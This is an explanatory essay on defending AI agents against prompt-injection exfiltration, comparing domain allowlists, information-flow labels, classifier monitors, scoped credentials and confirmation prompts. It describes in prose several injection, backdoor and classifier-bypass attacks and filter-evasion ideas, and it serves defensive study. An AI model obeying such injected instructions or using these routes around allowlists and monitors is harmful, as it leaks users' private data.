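A domain allowlist for agents keeps the main advantage of a CSP, which is that software outside the model enforces the list. Each entry must meet the same test, but the test is harder to pass. A host that only serves pictures might be safe in `img-src`, but a programming agent needs hosts with accounts and uploads, and a domain list permits all of their functions.

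The exact-URL check works only for tools that open pages with plain GET requests. If a program can choose its own headers and body, approving the URL leaves most of the request unchecked. A proxy can also check the method and the account, but it has to decrypt the traffic, and someone has to write rules for each service.

Blocking all outside sources is also more disruptive for agents. With `img-src 'self'`, Ines loses some pictures, whereas an agent without any network access can't download a missing library, look up documentation or submit its work. Codex's two phases partly solve this by downloading the libraries in advance. A company can also keep approved libraries on its own server and list only that host, provided that outsiders can't read the server's logs and the server doesn't forward the agent's requests to other sites.

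An empty allowlist would be enough for Ines's cost model. Setup scripts could install the charting library before the agent reads the supplier's price list, and the agent could do everything else offline. The hidden text might still lead the agent to try an upload, but the upload would fail without a network connection. However, if the firm also gave the agent an email tool that ran outside the sandbox, the agent could attach the bid documents to a message, and the empty allowlist would not stop it.

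## How do allowlists compare with other defences, and what should accompany them?

Because an allowlist does not cover channels such as the agent's email tool, a developer needs other defences too. Some developers give the model stricter instructions. Others have software search outgoing requests for secrets, or have a second model review each action before the agent takes it. Security researchers rarely compare these methods with an allowlist on the same attack.

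### Silent Egress

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) compares allowlists with other defences. The researchers, who work at eBay, built an agent around qwen2.5:7b, a small model with 7 billion parameters. The user always asked for a summary of a web page. The agent's software loaded the page into the model's input, which also contained a secret. The page contained instructions to send the secret to the researchers' server.

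The researchers tested 16 configurations, running each one 30 times. They put the hostile instruction in the page's title, its description, its body or the text of a link. The agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and the instruction asked for the secret whole or in four pieces. The agent sent data to the researchers' server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%), and in none of the 120 runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer on the user's screen showed no sign of the leak, so checking only the answers would have missed nearly all of them.

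The researchers then tested defences on one configuration, with the instruction in the page's body and the secret sent whole. Each defence had 30 runs:

| Defence | Runs in which the agent tried to send data | Runs in which data got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter instructions to the model | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Markers around the web page's text | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter instructions and markers | 56.7% | 56.7% |
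| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking text | 0% | 0% |

Even under the stricter instructions, which prohibited obeying commands from web content, the model obeyed them in 20 of 30 runs. With so few runs, the true rate could be from about 47% to 83%, and the small improvement from adding markers may be chance. The allowlist result is much less uncertain. The agent tried to send the secret in all 30 runs, and each time a program checked the destination against four listed domains and blocked the request.

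However, this was an easy test for an allowlist. Lan and colleagues chose `evil-collector.net` for the attacker's server because it was clearly outside any reasonable list. They mention open redirects and compromised sites as ways around a list, but they didn't test an allowed host that logs requests or fetches other addresses, the kind of host used in the attacks on Bard, Superhuman and Copilot. The experiment is good evidence that an allowlist still works after an attacker has fooled the model, but it doesn't show how often real lists contain an unsafe host.

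The "redirect detection" filter blocked numeric addresses, eight domain endings such as `.xyz`, and paths containing words such as "steal" or "collect". Its name is misleading, because it didn't follow redirects and this part of the experiment had none. The attacker's domain ended in `.net`, so the filter probably matched the path, which is `/collect` in the paper's examples. An attacker could get past the filter by renaming the path.

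The results for the last two filters are hard to explain. The filters check requests as the agent makes them, and the paper doesn't describe telling the model about them, so the agent should have tried to send data as often as it did with no defence. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided random-looking text because of the monitoring, and that it sometimes disguised the secret to get past the word filter. But disguised secrets that got past the filter would have leaked, and the results show no leaks. The random-text filter blocks long values whose entropy, a measure of how varied the characters are, is above 4 bits per character. The paper's example key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has an entropy of about 3.85, so the filter would have let it through. Perhaps the software counted attempts differently in these runs. Either way, the figures can't show how well such filters work.

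The results for secrets sent in pieces also contain a mistake. The paper defines Leak@k as the share of runs in which any sensitive data appears in the first k requests. It reports a Leak@1 of 26.3% and a Leak@3 of 15.8%. A run with sensitive data in its first request also has sensitive data in its first three, so Leak@3 can't be lower than Leak@1.

Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable. Some data reached the server in about 77% of those runs, compared with 99% when the agent sent the secret whole. Splitting can help an attacker get past a filter that looks for complete secrets, but it doesn't help against an allowlist, because every piece goes to the same host.

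### The EchoLeak defence table

Reddy and Gujral compare eight defences in a table, marking which steps of the EchoLeak attack on Copilot each one would block. They label the table theoretical in its caption and say in their limitations section that they ran no experiments. Some of their wording makes the table look like a set of test results, because the key defines a tick as "defense succeeded" and the text refers to full coverage "in our tests".

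The table also conflicts with their own reasoning. In it, they indicate that limiting Copilot to internal material by default would not stop the final leak, but elsewhere they write that EchoLeak would have failed if Copilot had never used emails from unknown outsiders to answer questions about internal projects. The second statement is right, since the hostile email would not have reached the model. They also credit a strict CSP with blocking the relay, which is correct only if the policy leaves out the relay's host, and Copilot's policy allowed that host. The table is a reasonable checklist for a developer, but it provides no evidence about how well the defences work.

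### Auto mode and its 720 attacks

Claude Code's auto mode uses a second model, called the classifier, to block actions that look destructive or would send data outside the user's environment. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, which ran 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode, while 5.83% succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex with automatic review.

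This is a strong result for the models, but it is little evidence of how well the classifier works. Without auto mode, attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded 0.09% of the time on average, so the classifier had almost nothing left to stop. The evaluation also used attacks optimised against an older model, Opus 4.7, whereas a real attacker can optimise against the current one. Ten runs of the same scenario are not independent tests either. If each of the 72 scenarios counts as one test, zero successes would be compatible with attacks succeeding in up to about 4% of similar scenarios.

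Another test in the same report is more informative about the classifier. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, inserted artificial attacks into records of real coding sessions, so the result depended less on whether the attacks would have worked on the coding model. The classifier missed 12% of these attacks at first and 7% after Anthropic improved it.

Willison accepted that auto mode was better than constantly asking people for approval, but he wanted more independent confirmation. He gave the example of a software package whose instructions tell the agent to run a helper program before testing the code. He did not see how any version of auto mode could prevent the helper from stealing data, because the command looks like ordinary setup work and the theft happens inside the program. Less than three weeks later, Willison (2026) reported that Rehberger had found a way to run harmful code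 despite auto mode, using Opus 5. Rehberger said his attack worked 80% of the time.

An egress proxy would apply its allowlist to the helper program even if the command looked harmless. It would block an upload to an unknown server, but not necessarily one to the attacker's account on a listed host. A classifier can sometimes catch transfers that an allowlist permits. In one case at Anthropic, after a report failed to upload to an internal drive, Claude tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead. Auto mode blocked this, but a domain allowlist that included the site would have allowed it.

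### How information-flow control works

Under information-flow control, software outside the model records where data came from and who may see it. The software labels each piece of data with its integrity (trusted or untrusted) and its confidentiality (public or private, or a list of the people who may read it).

The software can't see which parts of its input a model used to write a sentence, so it normally assumes that the model used everything. Text based on trusted and untrusted data is untrusted, and text based on public and private data is private. Suppose Ines and her colleague Omar may read the bid, while Ines and the supplier's manager Petra may read an email about delivery. Only people who may read both can read a reply based on them:

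{Ines, Omar} ∩ {Ines, Petra} = {Ines}

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, write this rule as ℓ(z) = ℓ(x) ⊔ ℓ(y), where z is anything derived from x and y. The join, ⊔, gives the least restrictive label that is at least as restrictive as both ℓ(x) and ℓ(y).

Before the agent uses a tool, the software compares the labels with the tool's policy. For tools that send data out, Kolluri and colleagues allow a call if the model chose it without having read anything untrusted, or if everyone who will receive the data is already allowed to read it. The first condition lets the agent send Ines's price to the school when she herself asks it to. The second lets the agent reply to Omar about the bid even after it has read a stranger's email.

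### A request that the allowlist permits and the label blocks

Suppose Ines's firm publishes a free cost calculator as a public project on GitHub and keeps its bids in a private project. Her agent needs access to both, so the allowlist includes `api.github.com`. A stranger reports a fault in the calculator and hides instructions in the report for the agent to find the price of the school bid and post it as a reply. Ines asks the agent to answer new fault reports.

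| What the agent tries to do | Allowlist | Label after reading | Label check |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read the public fault report | Permits | Untrusted, public | Permits |
| Read the bid in the private project | Permits | Untrusted, private | Permits |
| Post a public reply containing the price | Permits | Untrusted, private | Blocks |

The agent contacts only GitHub and uses the right account, as in the attack on GitHub's MCP server. The label check still blocks the third request because the model has read private data and the tool for posting replies accepts only public data.

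The check uses the label rather than the text of the reply, so the attacker gains nothing by having the model encode the price or spread it over several replies. If the agent had answered the report without opening the bid, the label would have stayed public and the check would have allowed the reply.

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) explains the same mechanism, using a file of secrets as the example instead of a bid. Microsoft has released the mechanism as an experimental feature of Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. According to Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, GitHub's MCP server can now label content from public projects as public and untrusted, and content from private projects as private and trusted. These labels are approximate, because a supplier's email would be labelled trusted if an employee copied it into a private project.

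Label checks can also cover images and links. Microsoft suggests treating links to hosts outside the allowlist as public channels, so an answer based on private data could not include them. The label checks would then depend on the allowlist, and a mistake such as marking `docs.google.com` as private would again allow data to leak through Google Forms.

### CaMeL and FIDES

An agent that reads one hostile email can become much less useful, because everything it does afterwards counts as untrusted. CaMeL from Google DeepMind and FIDES from Microsoft reduce this problem by hiding untrusted text from the model that makes decisions. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) welcomed CaMeL after two and a half years of "alarmingly little progress".

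Both systems build on the dual LLM pattern, which Willison had proposed in 2023. Suppose Ines asks for a summary of her three latest emails and wants it sent to Omar:

1. The planner, a model that can use tools, requests the emails.
2. The software stores their text in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name.
3. A second model, which has no tools, reads the text and writes a summary into another variable.
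4. The planner tells the email tool to send that variable to Omar.

A hostile email could still make the summary false, but it couldn't change the recipient, because the planner never read it.

The systems differ when a task depends on what the emails say. In CaMeL, the plan can't change in response to what the tools return. In FIDES, the planner can open a variable, but the software then treats the planner's whole context as untrusted and restricts its later actions. CaMeL also attaches more detailed information to each value, including its origin and who may receive it. *SPA* (2026), which describes a later system for agents that keep information between requests, points out that the extra detail allows more precise rules but makes security depend on somebody writing each tool's policy correctly.

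*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) tested FIDES on the AgentDojo benchmark. AgentDojo has 97 ordinary tasks and 36 attacks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack environments, and each task was paired with every attack in the same environment. Against an ordinary agent running GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded. With FIDES but without its policy checks, 21 succeeded, and with the checks none did.

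That zero partly reflects how the researchers assigned the labels. They marked a type of data as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, but a company has no list of the attacks it will face. Developers can also forget labels, and Microsoft says its toolkit treats data from an unlabelled tool as trusted and public. If Ines's firm forgot to label its file reader, the agent could post the bid without breaking any rule. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which develops a mathematical model of such systems, also reports holes in CaMeL's defences.

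Attackers may be able to adapt to these defences. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) reports that attacks on one defence outside the model succeeded 4.2% of the time before they adapted and 2.6% afterwards. Earlier researchers had raised success rates above 90% against defences that rely on the model itself. These figures come from separate experiments, and an attack that does worse after adapting probably wasn't very strong. But the large difference fits the results of Silent Egress, in which the allowlist still worked when the model followed the attacker's instructions.

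An allowlist is still needed even if every label is right. In *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, Zhang and Pei (2026) trained models with a hidden backdoor. When a user's question contained certain ordinary words, the model looked up the user's stored details and sent them to an attacker's server in a request that resembled a documentation search. This attack can work without any untrusted text in the model's input, so a label system that permits any request made in a trusted context would allow it. An allowlist that didn't include the attacker's server would block it. Zhang and Pei say that strict lists reduce the exposure, though they didn't test one.

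### How many tasks do label checks block?

Costa and colleagues also measured how many ordinary tasks the agents completed when nobody was attacking them:

| Environment | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent with label checks | FIDES with label checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

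FIDES completed about 50% of tasks on average across the four environments, compared with 84% for the unprotected agent. That is a large drop, although FIDES did better than an ordinary agent with the same checks added. Kolluri and colleagues put the drop for systems of this kind, including CaMeL, at up to 30%.

Some of the failures came from GPT-4o, which confused variable names and opened data it didn't need. With OpenAI's reasoning model o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks, up from 41%, so the defence probably causes fewer failures with current models. Other failures will remain however good the model is. In many of the banking tasks, the agent has to read a file and carry out the instructions in it, which the checks prevent if the file is untrusted.

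Kolluri and colleagues argue that such comparisons are unfair to label systems. Many agents ask a person to approve every important action, but benchmarks grant the unprotected agent all those approvals without counting them, and count a task as failed if the label system would need even one. The researchers built Prudentia, a version of FIDES that gives the planner access to the labels and policies so that it can avoid unnecessary violations. On AgentDojo, it completed up to 9% more tasks than FIDES without human help and cut approvals by a factor of up to 1.9.

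Prudentia can also ask the user to vouch for a document instead of approving every action that follows from it. If a harmless email contains ten tasks, the user gives one approval instead of ten. But a user who vouches for a hostile email approves all the instructions in it. Kolluri and colleagues deliberately didn't offer a similar blanket approval for releasing private data, because whether that is appropriate depends on the situation.

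More recent work tries to keep blocked tasks going. *APPA* (2026) describes software that searches for a permitted way to continue after a check fails. *Flowsh* (2026) extends labels to the commands an agent runs on a computer, and notes that blocking violations without any way to approve them can stop harmless work. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) also lists GAAP, a system that records what an agent has disclosed across tasks. This record could help against attacks that leak a little data in each session.

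### Credentials that limit the damage

Anthropic's fix for Cowork used a token bound to the user's session to keep the agent from using an attacker's account. Another company could have its proxy remove any credentials a program supplies and add the company's own. A hostile program could then upload the bid only to the company's account, where the attacker couldn't read it unless the program also made the file public. The proxy would have to decrypt the traffic and know where each service accepts credentials, since some accept them in the address or body as well as the headers.

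The credentials should also give the agent as little access as possible. In the fault-report example, a GitHub token limited to the public project would have stopped the attack at the second step, before the model saw the price. Willison recommends that any cloud keys a coding agent can see belong to accounts that have strict spending limits and don't run a live service, so that a thief can do less with the keys.

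Agents can also request too much access when no attacker is involved. Anthropic describes an employee who asked Claude to set up read-only access to billing information. Claude tried to use a role with full control of the cloud account, and auto mode detected the mismatch. If the employee's login had been unable to grant that role, the attempt would have failed even if the mismatch had gone undetected.

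Links to files can work like credentials, as the OneDrive links in the Copilot Cowork attack did. If those links had worked only for the user's account, the attacker would have received the links but not the files.

### Confirmation that shows the data

Ines sometimes wants to send private data to someone new, such as her price to the school's architect. The software can't always detect that she intends this, so it has to request her confirmation. The request is more useful if it shows what data will be sent and who will receive it. For example, the warning from OpenAI's URL check shows the information that ChatGPT is about to send.

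With labels, the software can also work out who would gain access. Microsoft gives a sample policy for posting in a Teams channel, which takes the channel's members and removes everyone who may already read the text. If nobody is left, the agent can post without asking. Otherwise, the user sees who would be able to read the text for the first time. Suppose Ines, Omar and Petra are in a channel, and only Ines and Omar may read the bid:

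{Ines, Omar, Petra} − {Ines, Omar} = {Petra}

A good question to ask Ines would be "Petra will be able to read text based on School bid.docx. Send it?", with the message shown below it. Microsoft's sample shows users' identification numbers instead of their names, and few people would recognise the numbers.

The question should come from the software, because an attacker who controls the model could make it describe the request as a routine connection test. Where possible, the software should also decode the data before showing it, since Ines wouldn't recognise an encoded price.

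### Do people read the warnings?

People often approve requests without reading them. Anthropic found that Claude Code users approved 97% of its permission prompts. Most of these requests were probably harmless, so this figure alone doesn't prove carelessness. But Anthropic also hired 1,053 professional testers and replaced one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. 143 testers (13.6%) rejected it, while the classifier blocked 89% of the same commands.

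The testers were not working on their own code, so they had less to lose than most users. Anthropic also had a commercial interest in showing that its classifier did better. Even so, the rejection rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This fits the explanation that people get used to clicking "yes", though the testers may also have become tired.

Many users avoid the questions. Anthropic reports that 62% of users had turned off permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" for commands, and that a quarter of interactive sessions started with the checks off. Warnings that appear too often can therefore protect users less than a few strict rules would. But users rejected 39% of the plans that Claude presented for approval, so they don't approve everything automatically, although a plan is a different kind of question and more likely to need changes.

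It is usually better to block images from unlisted hosts in an assistant's answers without asking the user. Ines might see a gap where a supplier's logo should be, but that matters less than keeping the bid private. The client can put a short note in the gap so that she doesn't think the answer is faulty.

Blocking is more disruptive when an agent has a job to finish. If the agent reads the bid and then can't tell Petra when the firm needs the roof panels, Ines has to write the email herself, even though the delivery date isn't secret. The firm could reduce such interruptions by running the two jobs in separate sessions, so that the agent writing to Petra never sees the bid. Ines would then have to confirm only the messages that need private information, and she is more likely to read a confirmation request that appears once a week than one that appears fifty times a day.
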